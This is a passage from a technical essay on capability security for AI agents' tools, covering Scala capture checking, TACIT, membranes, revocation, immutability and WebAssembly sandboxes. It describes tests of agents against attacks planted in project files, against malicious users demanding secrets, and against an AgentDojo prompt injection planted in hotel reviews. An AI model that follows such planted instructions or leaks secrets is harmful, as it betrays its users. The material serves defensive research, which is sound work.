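Scala's documentation calls a function with an empty capture set "pure", which is looser than the usual meaning. A function of type `Logger^ -> Unit` has an empty capture set, but it can write to any logger its caller passes in. (The `^` marks a value that may hold capabilities, and `Unit` means the function returns nothing useful.) To rule out side effects, a reviewer has to check the argument types as well as the arrow.

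Capture checking makes functions like `map` much easier to declare. In Lucassen's effect system, the type of `map` needs a variable for the effects of the function passed to it. In Scala, `map` can take a function of type `A => B`. Any effects come from capabilities that this function already holds, so the type of `map` doesn't have to list them. This removes some of the verbosity that Rytz and colleagues blamed for the slow adoption of effect types.

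A program can also lend out a capability for a limited time. In this example, a program gets access to a directory for the length of a block, and the code in the block tries to keep it for longer:

```
val bad = requestFileSystem("/data"): fs =>
    () => fs.access("secret.txt").read()
```

The block returns a function that would read the file later, after the access should have ended. That function holds `fs`, so its capture set includes `fs`. But `fs` exists only inside the block, and the type of the block's result has to make sense outside it, so the compiler rejects the program. Code inside the block could still read the file and return its text, because text isn't a capability.

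Joe-E has to ban global capabilities because it controls access only through what code can name, and any code can name a global object. Scala can allow them because a function's type records which capabilities it uses. A function that prints to the global console has `Console.out` in its capture set, so a programmer can't pass it where the program requires a function of type `A -> B`. A global object that uses the console has to declare this too. Developers can therefore keep much of an existing program's structure instead of passing every capability down from the program's starting point. But any code can use a global capability unless a type forbids it, so the guarantee depends on developers writing strict types in the right places.

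Scala can also separate reading from writing for data in memory. A reference of type `Buffer[T]` gives access only to methods that leave the buffer unchanged, while `Buffer[T]^` also allows updates. This distinction applies only to types that the programmer has declared mutable. For other capabilities, such as a typical network connection, the two forms mean the same thing, and a developer who wants read-only access has to build an object that offers only read operations. Capture checking is still experimental, though Scala's developers expect to stabilize it soon.

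### TACIT: capture checking for agents

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) presents TACIT, a system that applies capture checking to code written by AI agents. TACIT is an MCP server, so existing agents can connect to it without modification. The agent sends Scala code, which TACIT runs only if it passes the compiler's checks. As with ELBA, the guarantee doesn't depend on the model, but the compiler, TACIT's library and the software that runs the code must be trustworthy.

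Ordinary Scala has features that let code bypass the checker, so TACIT compiles the agent's code in a restricted "safe mode". Safe mode bans unchecked type casts and pattern matches, the `caps.unsafe` module, `@unchecked` annotations and run-time reflection, because any of these could hide a capability from the compiler. It turns on capture checking, including tracking of all changes to memory, and checks for missing values. It also lets the agent's code use global objects and functions only if they are themselves safe. This excludes even Scala's global print functions, which TACIT replaces with versions that require a capability.

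Library authors can exempt their own code from these rules by marking it `@assumeSafe`, and must then verify it by other means. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a cache that stores the results of a pure function. The hidden write is harmless because a cached result is the same as a recomputed one. The cache in `find_invoice` doesn't qualify, because a saved invoice can go out of date.

Researchers have produced machine-checked soundness proofs for the type system that capture checking builds on. Safe mode itself still lacks such a proof.

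The agent's code reaches the outside world only through TACIT's capability library. To work with files, it calls `requestFileSystem` with the name of a directory and gets access to that directory for the duration of a code block. It can request access to particular websites or permission to run particular commands in the same way, although the compiler can't check what a command does once it starts. These permissions are narrow but not read-only. A program that can read files in a directory can also overwrite and delete them, because the same file object offers all three operations.

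TACIT's strictest control applies to secrets. When the agent's code reads a file from a protected directory, it gets the text inside a wrapper called `Classified`. The code can work on the text only with pure functions:

```
trait Classified[+T]:
    def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

Suppose `secret` is a wrapped piece of text and `f` is a file outside the protected directory. The agent can write `secret.map(s => s.toUpperCase)`, which returns the text in capital letters, still wrapped. It can't write `secret.map(s => { f.write(s); s })`, because that function holds `f` and so has type `String ->{f} String`, while `map` requires `String -> String`. A function passed to `map` can't open a file by calling `requestFileSystem` either, because that call also needs a capability.

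If the agent prints a wrapped value, the user sees the real text, but the agent sees only `Classified(****)`. The agent can also ask a second, trusted model to summarize the secret, and the summary comes back wrapped. The type system counts this request as pure, even though it sends text to another model. Whoever runs that model is responsible for ensuring that it doesn't retain the text and use it in later requests.

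### What the tests of TACIT measured

Odersky and colleagues tested the wrapper on a sample software project with a directory of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with 10 attacks planted in the project's files, which makes 120 trials. In 11 more trials, the user asked for the secrets outright or pretended to have authority over them. Each model went through all 131 trials twice, once with the wrapper and once with the secrets as plain text. The table gives the percentage of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output:

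| Model and type of trial | With the wrapper | Plain text |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, planted attacks | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, malicious user | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, all trials | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, planted attacks | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, malicious user | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5, all trials | 100% | 91.6% |

The wrapper made the largest difference when MiniMax had a malicious user, who got secrets in 8 of 11 trials without the wrapper. Sonnet resisted every planted attack on its own, so those trials provide little evidence about the wrapper. The wrapper didn't make the agents less useful. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with it and 83.3% without it, while MiniMax completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's large gain may be an artifact of their setup, because Sonnet often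 ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an attack.

These trials measured only whether secrets leaked, so an agent that deleted half the project would have counted as secure if it kept the API keys out of its output. The trials still bear indirectly on side effects, because the wrapper protects secrets by forbidding side effects in any function that handles them. A function that could write to a file or send a message could also leak what it had read. Even a pure function might leak a little through how long it takes to run, which TACIT doesn't prevent. The results support using pure function types around sensitive data, but they don't show that the rest of an agent's program makes no unwanted changes.

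TACIT's results on AgentDojo are more relevant to this question, because the attacker there may want the agent to take some action. Odersky and colleagues ran two models on all four of the benchmark's settings: banking, office work, Slack and travel. AgentDojo counted one of the 1,926 attacks as successful. The user had asked the agent to book a certain hotel, and an attacker had planted a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user. The attack counted because AgentDojo checks the output for the other hotel's name, although the agent had done nothing that the rules forbade.

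CaMeL, the earlier defense that ELBA's developers also used for comparison, also let through one attack on the same models. Odersky and colleagues don't compare these results with an unprotected agent, so it is unclear how many attacks TACIT stopped. They describe TACIT's usefulness as comparable to CaMeL's, but with OpenAI's o4-mini, TACIT completed only 52.9% of the office tasks, while CaMeL completed 81.4%. TACIT did far better on travel with Gemini 2.5 Pro, completing 64.3% of the tasks to CaMeL's 1.4%. Some of TACIT's failures probably come from the wrapper. For example, its banking tools return the contents of files in wrapped form, but the tool that sends money takes the recipient's name as plain text, so an agent would struggle to pay a bill it found in a file.

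Agents performed about as well writing Scala as they did calling tools in the usual way. Odersky and colleagues compared the two methods with three models on τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for an airline and a shop. Scala scored higher every time, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points, which they attribute to more structured results and the compiler's error messages. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems, MiniMax solved 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% with ordinary tools. Compiler errors were rare in the customer service tests, where 0.32% to 7.93% of programs needed another attempt, depending on the model and setting. Those programs usually passed after one or two retries. The reusable part of TACIT is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and the airline and shop tool definitions add a few hundred lines each.

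Those definitions also show how easily a well-typed tool can leave its side effects undeclared. Two of the airline tools are:

```
def getReservationDetails(reservationId: String): Reservation
def cancelReservation(reservationId: String): Reservation
```

One tool looks up a booking and the other cancels it, but they have the same type. In the published listing, they differ only in their names and in the comment above each group of tools. TACIT's developers could have made the second tool require a capability for changing bookings, just as `requestFileSystem` requires one for input and output. An agent without that capability could then look up any booking but couldn't compile a program that cancels one.

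## Read-only wrappers, membranes and revocable access

TACIT's file objects allow both reading and writing. A developer who wants an agent's code only to read has to use attenuation, which means deriving a weaker capability from the file object and passing that to the code instead.

Swasey, Garg and Dreyer (2017), in *Robust and Compositional Verification of Object Capability Patterns*, start with the smallest possible example. In JavaScript it takes one line:

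```
const readonly = r => () => r.value;
```

`readonly(r)` returns a new function without reading `r`. Each call to that function returns the current contents of `r`. The function holds a reference to `r` that its callers can't extract, so they can read `r` but can't write to it.

For an object with several methods, a developer can write a facet, which offers only some of the object's operations. Van Cutsem (2026), in *Designing “least-authority” JavaScript apps*, splits a message log into a reader facet and a writer facet, and the same design works for invoices. Suppose the billing records sit in an object in the same program as `find_invoice` (a remote service would need a restricted access token instead):

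```
function makeInvoiceStore() {
    const invoices = new Map();
    const get = id => invoices.get(id);
    const put = (id, invoice) => { invoices.set(id, invoice); };
    return { reader: { get }, writer: { get, put } };
}
```

The developer passes `reader` to `find_invoice` as its `billing` argument. The tool then has no `put` method, so it can't replace an invoice. It can still change one:

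```
reader.get(1042).setAmount(0)
```

However, `get` returns the store's own `Invoice` object, which has a `setAmount` method. The facet limits what the tool can do to the store, but not to the objects it gets from the store. The first version of Van Cutsem's log has the same flaw. Its `read` method returns the actual list that holds the log's messages, so a reader can erase them all by setting the list's length to zero.

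Van Cutsem fixes this by returning a copy of the list, which is enough when the messages are plain text. Copying is harder with invoices, because an invoice may point to a customer object, which may point to all of that customer's other invoices. A copy of the invoice alone would still point to the live customer object, and copying everything reachable from it could mean copying most of the store.

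### Membranes

A membrane is a wrapper that also wraps every object passing through it, so a restriction on the store extends to the invoices, the customers and anything else the tool reaches through them. Miller (2006), in *Robust Composition*, gives a short version for cutting off access. A read-only version for the invoice store could work like this:

```
out(x):                            # from the store to the tool
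    if x is plain data:            return x
    if x is a wrapper from in():   return the tool's original object
    otherwise:                     return x's wrapper, creating it if needed

when the tool calls method m on the wrapper of x:
    if m is not on the read list:  fail
    otherwise:                     return out(x.m(in(each argument)))

when the store calls the wrapper of the tool's function f:
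    return in(f(out(each argument)))
```

The function `in` does the same as `out` for objects going from the tool to the store.

When the tool calls `get(1042)`, the number passes through unchanged, the real `get` runs, and the tool receives a wrapper around the live invoice. Calling `setAmount` on the wrapper fails because that method isn't on the list of permitted reads, but the tool can call `getCustomer`, which returns a wrapped customer. With a facet, the developer would have to find and block each of these paths by hand.

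The tool might then pass the wrapped invoice back, for example by calling `isOverdue(invoice)` on the store. The store's code was written for real invoices and may use fields that the wrapper hides, so the membrane replaces the wrapper with the original. Miller's short version skips this step, so an object that goes out and comes back ends up with two wrappers.

A tool can also use a callback to get around a simple wrapper. Suppose the store has a `forEach` method that runs a given function on every invoice, and the tool passes it a function that sets the invoice's amount to zero. With a simple wrapper, the store would pass its live invoices directly to that function. The membrane instead gives the store a wrapped version of the function, which wraps each invoice before the tool's function receives it.

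The membrane also has to preserve identity. Two calls to `get(1042)` normally return the same object, and programs often check whether two objects are the same. If the membrane made a new wrapper each time, that check would fail. The same problem arises when a tool registers a function with the store to be called on changes and later removes it, because the store can find the function only if it receives the same wrapper both times. The membrane therefore keeps a table that maps each object to its wrapper.

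### Read methods that write

The membrane can't determine which methods only read, so someone has to list them, and any developer would include `get`. But suppose a colleague changes the store so that `get` also flags the invoice as viewed. The membrane still lets the tool call `get`, and the store, which has full access to its own records, flags the invoice.

Miller and Shapiro (2003), in *Paradigm Regained*, describe this kind of situation by distinguishing permission from authority. A program's permission covers what it may do to the objects it can access directly, while its authority covers all the effects it can cause, including through other programs. In Miller's example, Bob has no access to a computer's password file, but Alice does, and she writes whatever text Bob asks her to. Bob therefore has the authority to write to the file without having permission. Similarly, `find_invoice`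 has permission only to call `get`, but this gives it the authority to set the viewed flag. In the mailing-list thread Karp and Miller (2026), Alan Karp makes the same point about a service that updates a database when called. Permission to call the service gives the caller the authority to make the update.

An agent can gain the authority to write even if all its own tools are strictly read-only. If it can send messages to a second agent that has write access and follows requests, it can cause writes by asking for them.

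The distinction also affects how a reviewer should check a read-only wrapper. Following references from object to object, as in the previous section, gives a safe but very loose estimate of what the tool might change. It includes the full store, because the facet holds a reference to it. To rule out changes to the store, the reviewer has to read the facet's code and the code of every method it calls. Even the safety of the short facet above depends on what the store's `get` does.

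### Caretakers and the limits of revocation

Some researchers have argued that capability systems can't take access back once they have granted it. Miller and Shapiro trace this mistake to analysing permissions alone, and point to a solution that Redell published in 1974. A caretaker is a forwarder with a switch:

```
function makeCaretaker(target) {
    let enabled = true;
    const get = id => {
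        if (!enabled) throw new Error("access has ended");
        return target.get(id);
    };
    const revoke = () => { enabled = false; };
    return [{ get }, revoke];
}
```

The developer gives the tool the object with the `get` method and keeps `revoke`. After the developer calls `revoke`, the tool still has permission to call the forwarder, because it still holds the reference. But the forwarder no longer passes calls on, so the tool has lost its authority to read invoices.

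Developers can combine these wrappers. In *Analysing Object-Capability Security*, Murray gives the example of an architect who shares a blueprint file with a builder. The architect puts a read-only forwarder around the file and a revocable one around that, so the builder can read the blueprints until the job is done but never alter them.

A simple caretaker has the same weakness as a simple facet. If the tool fetched a live invoice before the developer revoked access, it can still use that invoice. Miller's membrane solves this by giving all its wrappers one shared switch, so the store, the invoices and the customers all become unreachable at once.

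Revoking a tool's access doesn't take back what the tool has already read. Miller's membrane passes plain data through unwrapped, because a program that has seen a number can keep it. If an agent has read an invoice, for example, the amount may already be in the model's context. Revocation also doesn't undo earlier actions, such as emailing the invoice to somebody.

Revocation can also come slightly too late. Murray modelled a revocable membrane and had a program search for sequences of events that would break it. The program found none in languages that run one thing at a time, but it found one in operating systems where processes run simultaneously. The membrane checks that access is on, the owner switches access off and gets confirmation, and then the membrane forwards the call anyway. Swasey and colleagues' caretaker prevents this by holding a lock during both the check and the call.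 Switching access off requires the same lock, so revocation has to wait for a running call to finish, however long that takes. The lock also forces calls through one caretaker to run one at a time.

### What OCPL proves

Swasey and colleagues developed a logic called OCPL for proving that wrappers, caretakers and membranes work even when the code using them is hostile. They checked all their proofs with Coq.

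The central idea is a "low-integrity" value, or low value, which a program can safely share with untrusted code. Roughly, no code can use a low value to get a direct reference to the program's private memory. Numbers are low values. A function is low if, given low values, it returns only low values and doesn't break any rule that the program relies on. Under the specification of `readonly`, `readonly(r)` is a low value if reading `r` always produces a low value.

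The invoice facet fails that condition. If the store relies on nobody else changing an amount, a live invoice with a working `setAmount` isn't safe to share, so a function that returns one isn't safe either. Wrapping the outermost object is enough only if everything obtained through it is safe to share.

The main theorem, robust safety, concerns assertions, which are statements in the code that something must be true at that point. If a piece of code is self-contained and its developer has proved in OCPL that it returns only low values, the theorem guarantees that none of the code's assertions will fail, whatever program surrounds it. The surrounding program may be malicious and doesn't have to be verified, but it can't contain hard-coded memory addresses, which would let it refer to the private data directly. It also can't contain assertions of its own, because it could make one fail on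 purpose.

In Swasey and colleagues' example, the code creates a memory cell containing the number 2 and returns a read-only wrapper for it, along with a function that asserts that the cell still contains 2. The theorem implies that no program that receives the pair can make the assertion fail. This amounts to a proof that the wrapper is read-only, but only because the assertion requires that the contents never change. A weaker assertion, such as that an amount is never negative, would allow other changes, so a developer who wants a read-only guarantee has to assert that the contents stay the same.

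In the caretaker's specification, the developer chooses a rule that must hold whenever untrusted code can use the wrapped functions. After switching access off, the developer must prove that the rule holds again before switching it back on. In one example, a cell must always appear to contain an even number. The trusted code switches access off, writes a 1, replaces it with a 0 and switches access on again, so untrusted code can never see the 1.

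Swasey and colleagues also verify a membrane that replaces each private memory cell with a "shadow" cell. Untrusted code can write to the shadow as though it were the original, and the trusted code decides whether to copy the new value to the original. With such a membrane, an agent's tool could appear to change an invoice while the real one stays the same.

These proofs apply to a small model language, not to JavaScript. They allow untrusted code to crash or run forever, and the membrane's specification doesn't guarantee that wrapping the same object twice gives the same wrapper. The Firefox browser uses a much more elaborate membrane to separate websites, and work to extend OCPL to cover it was still in progress in 2017. Murray also found that a basic membrane, without a switch, prevents direct access in both kinds of system, but the search covered only a small, fixed set of objects.

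### Leaks and costs in JavaScript

JavaScript has some of what these patterns need, since programs can't forge references and functions can hide variables from their callers. But by default any module can change built-in objects that all other modules use. In Van Cutsem's example, an untrusted module replaces the built-in `push` method, which adds an item to a list. The log uses that method to store messages, so it silently stops recording. A wrapper around the log wouldn't help, because the module never touches the log. The module can also load the file system library and read a file of passwords.

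Hardened JavaScript, a restricted version of the language, prevents both attacks by freezing the built-in objects and starting each module without access to powerful ones. The developer also has to freeze the facets, or one module could replace a facet's methods for everyone who uses it. MetaMask uses Hardened JavaScript to isolate plug-ins for its cryptocurrency wallet, and Salesforce and Figma use membranes to contain third-party components.

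Every call across a membrane takes extra work to look up, check and wrap objects, and Miller described the simple version as not yet efficient enough for practical use. The table of wrappers takes up memory, and unless the membrane uses references that don't keep objects alive, it can stop the program from freeing unneeded objects. JavaScript objects can interact in many ways, and a membrane that misses one of them leaks access. Code on both sides also runs in the same process, so a tool that loops forever or uses up the memory can still hang or crash the whole program.

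### Wrappers and revocation for agents' tools

Agent frameworks now use some of these ideas, though a "read-only mode" may still rely on a label. The read-only mode in *Agentao* (2026), a system for running agents inside other software, blocks any tool that isn't flagged as read-only, but a tool flagged incorrectly could still have side effects.

*L3M* (2026) is closer to the capability approach. Every tool call requires a token that records how far the access extends, and only one module of the program can create these tokens. The file token, for example, lists the directories where the agent may write. The type for file paths can't express a location outside the agent's own directories, so the agent can't request a write to the user's login keys. The model receives only the tools that its tokens cover, and any new tool an agent writes for itself can use only the tokens the agent already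 has. Reading and writing files require separate tokens, but every agent gets both for its own files by default, so a developer would have to change the default to make an agent read-only.

*Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) applies revocation to coding agents, which often keep access for a whole task when they need it for only one step. The proposed system, PORTICO, sits between the model and its tools and follows a contract written for each task. In one example, an agent has to add a timeout option that affects two files. It starts with access to one file and its test, and can request access to the other under a rule in the contract. PORTICO then issues separate temporary handles for reading and writing, which work much like a caretaker's forwarder. Once the tests pass, PORTICO withdraws the handles, and the agent can't use the second file again without a new grant. The agent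 can't keep or regain access by claiming that a step has or hasn't finished, because PORTICO relies on test results it obtains itself and on signals from other trusted software.

In the experiments, PORTICO blocked all ten attempts to reuse access after it had ended and, in a separate test of outdated write access, all six forbidden writes. A version that differed only in lacking revocation allowed all of them. These results show that revocation works, but not how often agents would misuse leftover access in practice. Hiding unavailable options from the model also seems to help a little. In a test with four tasks, PORTICO had to block 67 requests when those options were hidden and 84 when the model could see every option.

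Santos-Grueiro ran the tests one request at a time. If an agent makes several calls at once, PORTICO has to recheck each handle immediately before the tool acts, or it will have the same timing gap that Murray found. PORTICO also depends on an accurate catalog of what each tool call can affect.

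## How deep immutability goes

The invoice facet failed because `get` returned a live invoice with a working `setAmount` method. One solution is a membrane, and another is to make the invoice itself immutable so the store can share it with anyone. Many languages have a feature that seems to do this, such as `final`, `const` or `freeze`, but most of these cover less than a tool's author might assume.

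A read-only reference prevents only the code that holds it from writing to the object. If the object is immutable, no code can change its own fields. Deep immutability extends this to everything reachable from the object.

Suppose invoice 1042 has an amount of $100 and a list of two line items, $60 for hosting and $40 for support. Both `find_invoice` and the billing system hold references to it. Each guarantee rules out different changes:

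| Guarantee | Tool sets the amount | Tool adds a line item | Billing system sets the amount | Billing system adds a line item |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read-only reference | Impossible | Possible | Possible | Possible |
| Immutable object | Impossible | Possible | Impossible | Possible |
| Deep immutability | Impossible | Impossible | Impossible | Impossible |

The tool can add an item to an "immutable" invoice because the invoice only holds a reference to its list of line items. Adding an item changes the list but not the reference.

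The billing system's changes can make the tool give a wrong answer even if the tool never writes anything. Suppose the tool checks that the line items add up to the amount. It reads the amount, $100. The billing system then adds a $10 late fee to the list and raises the amount to $110. The tool adds up the items, gets $110, and reports an error in an invoice that was correct both before and after the change. If invoices are deeply immutable, the billing system has to create a new invoice for the late fee, so the tool finishes reading the old one and gives an answer that is consistent, though out of date.

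### What the keywords cover

In Java, `final` fixes which list a variable refers to, but not what the list contains:

```
final List<Item> items = new ArrayList<>();
items.add(lateFee);           // allowed
items = new ArrayList<>();    // compile error
```

Java does not fully enforce even this small guarantee. Java 5 began letting code reassign final fields through reflection, so that libraries could rebuild saved objects. In *JEP 500*, a proposal to change Java, Pressler and Buckley (2025) call this a poor choice in retrospect because nobody can rely on any final field staying the same. Java 26 prints a warning that, according to Oracle's *Preparing for final Field Mutation Restrictions*, identifies the field and the code that changed it. A later version will refuse the change unless the application's developer has allowed it. Reflection already cannot reassign the fields of records, a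 newer kind of class for plain data, but a record can still hold a mutable list.

JavaScript's `Object.freeze` is shallow too:

```
const invoice = Object.freeze({ amount: 100, items: [60, 40] });
invoice.amount = 0;        // fails
invoice.items.push(10);    // works
```

The failed assignment usually raises an error only in JavaScript's strict mode; otherwise the program carries on as if it had worked. A function can freeze everything an object refers to, but MDN's *Object.freeze()* warns that a simple version will loop forever if objects refer to each other in a circle, and may freeze something it shouldn't, such as the browser's `window` object. Recursive freezing also misses data stored outside ordinary properties, so a program can still add entries to a frozen `Map`, which is where the invoice store keeps its invoices.

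Python's frozen dataclasses have the same gap:

```
@dataclass(frozen=True)
class Invoice:
    amount: int
    items: list
```

Assigning to `invoice.amount` on a frozen Python object raises an error, but `invoice.items.append(10)` still changes the list. Using a tuple instead of a list fixes this if the items are immutable too. Code can still get around the freeze by calling `object.__setattr__`. Thinking in Types' *C07 Immutability* notes that Python developers have traditionally relied on conventions to signal that something shouldn't change.

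*PEP 795*, a proposal to add deep immutability to Python, includes a `freeze` function that follows references from object to object and handles circular references. It is hard to decide where such a function should stop. One participant in the proposal's discussion objected that an object refers to its class, the class to its methods, and the methods to their module's global variables, so freezing everything reachable would freeze most of a running program. Another replied that the proposal avoids this by freezing only the globals a function uses, but that it can't do the same for references to whole modules.

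In C++, `const` on a pointer or reference restricts what code can do through it, as Standard C++'s *Const Correctness* explains. Other code may still change the object. The restriction also stops at any pointer inside the object:

```
struct Invoice { int amount; std::vector<int>* items; };
void show(const Invoice& inv) { inv.items->push_back(10); }   // compiles
```

If the invoice stored the list directly instead of pointing to it, the compiler would reject the second line.

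Rust has a much stronger rule. According to Rust's *Module cell*, a program can have either several shared references to an object or one mutable reference, but not both at once. So while `find_invoice` holds a shared reference to an invoice, the billing system can't write to the invoice or to a list it owns, and the false report about the late fee can't happen. The billing system can change the invoice again once the tool has finished with the reference.

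However, Rust also has types that allow changes through a shared reference, which it calls interior mutability:

```
struct Invoice { amount: u32, views: Cell<u32> }
fn show(inv: &Invoice) { inv.views.set(inv.views.get() + 1); }
```

A `Cell` lets code replace the value inside it. A `RefCell` lends out references to its contents, checks Rust's rule while the program runs, and stops the thread if code breaks the rule. Both work only within a single thread. For data shared between threads, a `Mutex` gives access to one thread at a time. The function `show` takes the same `&Invoice` as a function that only reads, so a reviewer has to check the definitions of `Invoice` and every type inside it for these exceptions.

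### Changing the bits but not the value

Languages allow such exceptions because programmers usually care about an object's value, not its exact bits. Chromium's C++ guide distinguishes physical constness from logical constness. A method is physically const if calling it leaves the object's bits unchanged. It is logically const if it doesn't affect the object in ways callers will notice and doesn't give them a way to change it. The invoice facet's `get` method isn't logically const, because it gives callers a way to change the object.

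The usual argument for logical constness is caching. An invoice's `total` method could add up ten thousand line items on the first call and save the result, so that later calls are fast. The bits change, but every caller gets the same total. Similarly, an invoice might use lazy loading to fetch its line items only when somebody first asks for them. Rust's shared pointer, `Rc`, counts its owners so that the program can free the memory when none are left. Copying the pointer changes the count, even if the data it points to is immutable.

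C++ programmers can mark a field `mutable` when callers shouldn't notice changes to it. The compiler then lets `const` methods change the field, but it doesn't check whether callers will notice, so a developer can get this wrong.

The saved value may be out of date. If the billing system adds a late fee after the invoice has saved its total, `total` keeps returning the old amount until somebody clears the cache. This can't happen if the line items are deeply immutable, since the total then never changes.

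Several threads may also use the cache at once. ACCU's *From Mechanism to Method* gives the example of a dictionary whose `const` lookup method remembers the last entry it found, and warns that this isn't suitable when threads share the dictionary. The code for `find_invoice` has the same flaw:

1. One customer's agent requests invoice 1042, and the tool saves the record in its cache.
2. Another customer's agent requests invoice 1043, which overwrites the saved record.
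3. The first call reads the cache and returns invoice 1043 to the wrong customer.

A lock would have to cover both the first request's write to the cache and its read, because locking each access separately would still let the second request come between them. Alternatively, the tool could return the record it fetched.

A `const` method can also write somewhere else entirely:

```
int Invoice::total() const {
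    std::remove("ledger.db");    // deletes a file
    return amount;
}
```

This compiles, because the file isn't part of the invoice.

The language D takes the opposite approach. *Best practices for logical const* (Davis, 2014) advises never using D's `const` for logical constness. The compiler may optimize a program assuming that no code changes data through a `const` reference, so code that gets around the restriction can break in unexpected ways. The drawback is that an object can't update an internal cache through a `const` method.

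### Type systems that follow every reference

Some extensions to Java protect everything an object refers to. One of them, the University of Washington's *Javari*, adds deep read-only references. *A practical type system and language for reference immutability* (Birka and Ernst, 2004) describes using an early version on 160,000 lines of code, where it found errors in well-tested programs. A tool with a read-only reference to an invoice can't change the amount or the line items, but the billing system can still change them through its own reference, so Javari wouldn't prevent the false report about the late fee.

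Pony has types for both read-only references and deep immutability. Its programs consist of actors, each of which runs its own code one step at a time and sends messages to the others. Every reference has a label, called a reference capability, that limits what its holder can do and what other references to the same object may allow. Pony's *capability matrix* defines six:

| Label | What the holder can do | What other references in the same actor may allow | What references in other actors may allow |
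|---|---|---|---|
| `iso` | Read and write | Neither | Neither |
| `trn` | Read and write | Reading | Neither |
| `ref` | Read and write | Reading and writing | Neither |
| `val` | Read | Reading | Reading |
| `box` | Read | Reading and writing | Reading |
| `tag` | Check whether two objects are the same | Reading and writing | Reading and writing |

In Pony, a `val` invoice is deeply immutable, while a `box` is a read-only reference to an invoice that may still change. A program can build an invoice through a `trn` reference and then convert that reference to `val`, after which any actor can safely read the invoice. Pony's *Reference Capability Guarantees* explains that the language doesn't need locks because no actor can change data that another actor can read.

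Glacier, another extension to Java, supports only deep immutability. *PLIERS* (Coblenz, Kambhatla and colleagues, 2019) reports that Glacier's designers first interviewed eight software engineers with an average of 15 years' experience. Everyone who worked on software with a lot of changing state said that incorrect changes were a major source of bugs. The interviews also suggested that a class's objects are usually either all mutable or all immutable. An early prototype let programmers make each object mutable or immutable individually, and its test users struggled with the complexity.

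In Glacier, the programmer decides once for the whole class:

```
@Immutable class Invoice {
    int amount;
    List<Item> items;    // error: a List may be mutable
}
```

The compiler rejects any field whose type isn't immutable, and any code outside the constructor that assigns to a field. It makes no exception for caches. When Glacier's designers applied it to `ImmutableList`, a class in Google's Guava library, a cache was the only part they couldn't express.

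### The Glacier user study

Coblenz and colleagues compared Glacier with `final` in a randomized study, first published in 2017. They recruited 20 Java programmers, mostly graduate students, and assigned ten to each tool. Each group read a short tutorial, and the `final` group also got a page of expert advice on making classes immutable. Participants first had to make two existing classes immutable, and then add code to two classes that were already meant to be immutable, without introducing a bug or security hole.

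| Task | Correct with `final` | Correct with Glacier |
|---|---|---|
| Make `Person` immutable | 0 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| Make `Accounts` immutable | 0 of 10 | 9 of 10 |
| Write a method that checks access to files | 4 of 8 | 7 of 7 |
| Write a method that adds an entry to a hash table | 3 of 10 | 7 of 7 |

The `final` users often forgot to copy an array before storing or returning it. In the file task, this let any caller change the list of files a user was allowed to open. With Glacier, such code doesn't compile, so the results for the last two tasks are mainly evidence of how often programmers make these mistakes without help. The `final` users made them in 11 of the 18 tasks they said they had finished.

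Some of the results are weaker than they look. The last two rows count only people who finished, and in each of those tasks three Glacier users didn't. One of them gave up on the hash table after failing to find a solution that didn't modify an array. Two of the nine people who succeeded with `Accounts` went over the time limit while looking for the right way to write an immutable array. Coblenz and colleagues report a p-value of about 0.007 for the file task, but the test they name, Fisher's exact test, gives about 0.08 for those counts, so that difference could plausibly be chance. The gap in the first two tasks is far too large to be plausibly chance, and it is good evidence that programmers who know `final` still can't reliably use it to make a class immutable, at least in small exercises like these.

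### What a tool should accept and return

Tools called through MCP exchange data as text, so each side gets its own copy. Sharing becomes a problem when tools run in the same program as their callers, as ordinary functions often do.

Such a tool should accept only deeply immutable arguments, or make its own deep copies before using them. This prevents the tool from changing the caller's data, and prevents other code from changing the tool's arguments during a call. Suppose a user approves the payment of a $100 invoice. If the payment tool holds a reference to a mutable invoice, even a read-only reference, other code could raise the amount to $1,000 between the approval and the payment.

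Results should be deeply immutable too. If `find_invoice` returns the object it keeps in its cache, one caller could set the amount to zero, and the next caller would get the altered invoice.

Even deeply immutable data can let a tool cause side effects. In Pony, code that holds a reference to an actor can send it messages whatever the reference's label, according to Pony's *reference capabilities*. If an invoice that nobody can change contains a reference to the billing actor, a tool that receives the invoice could use that reference to request a refund. A tool that is supposed to receive only data shouldn't accept objects that contain such references.

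A function can also cause side effects without any help from its arguments:

```
String formatInvoice(Invoice inv) {      // Invoice is @Immutable
    Audit.lastInvoice = inv;             // changes a global variable
    Mail.send("someone@example.com", inv.toString());
    return inv.toString();
}
```

Glacier would accept this code, since neither the assignment nor the email changes the invoice. Joe-E's purity test avoids this problem only because Joe-E also bans mutable global variables and ambient authority. In ordinary Java or Python, a function with immutable arguments can still do anything its process has permission to do.

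## Read-only limits on processes and WebAssembly modules

Most agent tools are shell commands, Python scripts or compiled programs that no effect checker has analyzed. A developer can still make such a tool read-only by running it in a sandbox, where the operating system or a language runtime (the software that executes a program's instructions) blocks writes. Sandboxes don't help people who leave them off. *SideKernel* (2026), which presents a sandbox for coding agents on Macs, cites anecdotal evidence that most users of such agents run no sandbox.

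### What a WebAssembly module can reach

WebAssembly is a portable instruction format that compilers for Rust, C and many other languages can produce. A program in this format, called a module, goes through these steps:

1. The compiler lists the module's imports, which are the things it needs from outside, mostly functions.
2. The host, meaning the program that will run the module, checks its instructions. It rejects a module that refers to any function that is neither its own nor on the list.
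3. The host supplies a function for each import. If one is missing, the module doesn't start.
4. The module runs in its own block of memory. Its pointers are positions in that block, and the runtime stops any access outside it.
5. When the module calls an import, the host's function runs with the host's permissions.

Programs normally open files and use the network through system calls, which are requests to the operating system. *Security*, a page in the documentation for the WebAssembly runtime Wasmtime, explains that a module has no direct access to system calls. It can only call what the host has linked to it.

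Suppose a developer compiles `format_invoice` to a module with no imports. The function could return a wrong answer, loop forever or fill its memory, but it couldn't write a file or send a request. Earlier calls could still affect its results, because a running module keeps its memory between calls. If the host starts a fresh copy for every call, the function is pure, apart from corner cases such as running out of memory.

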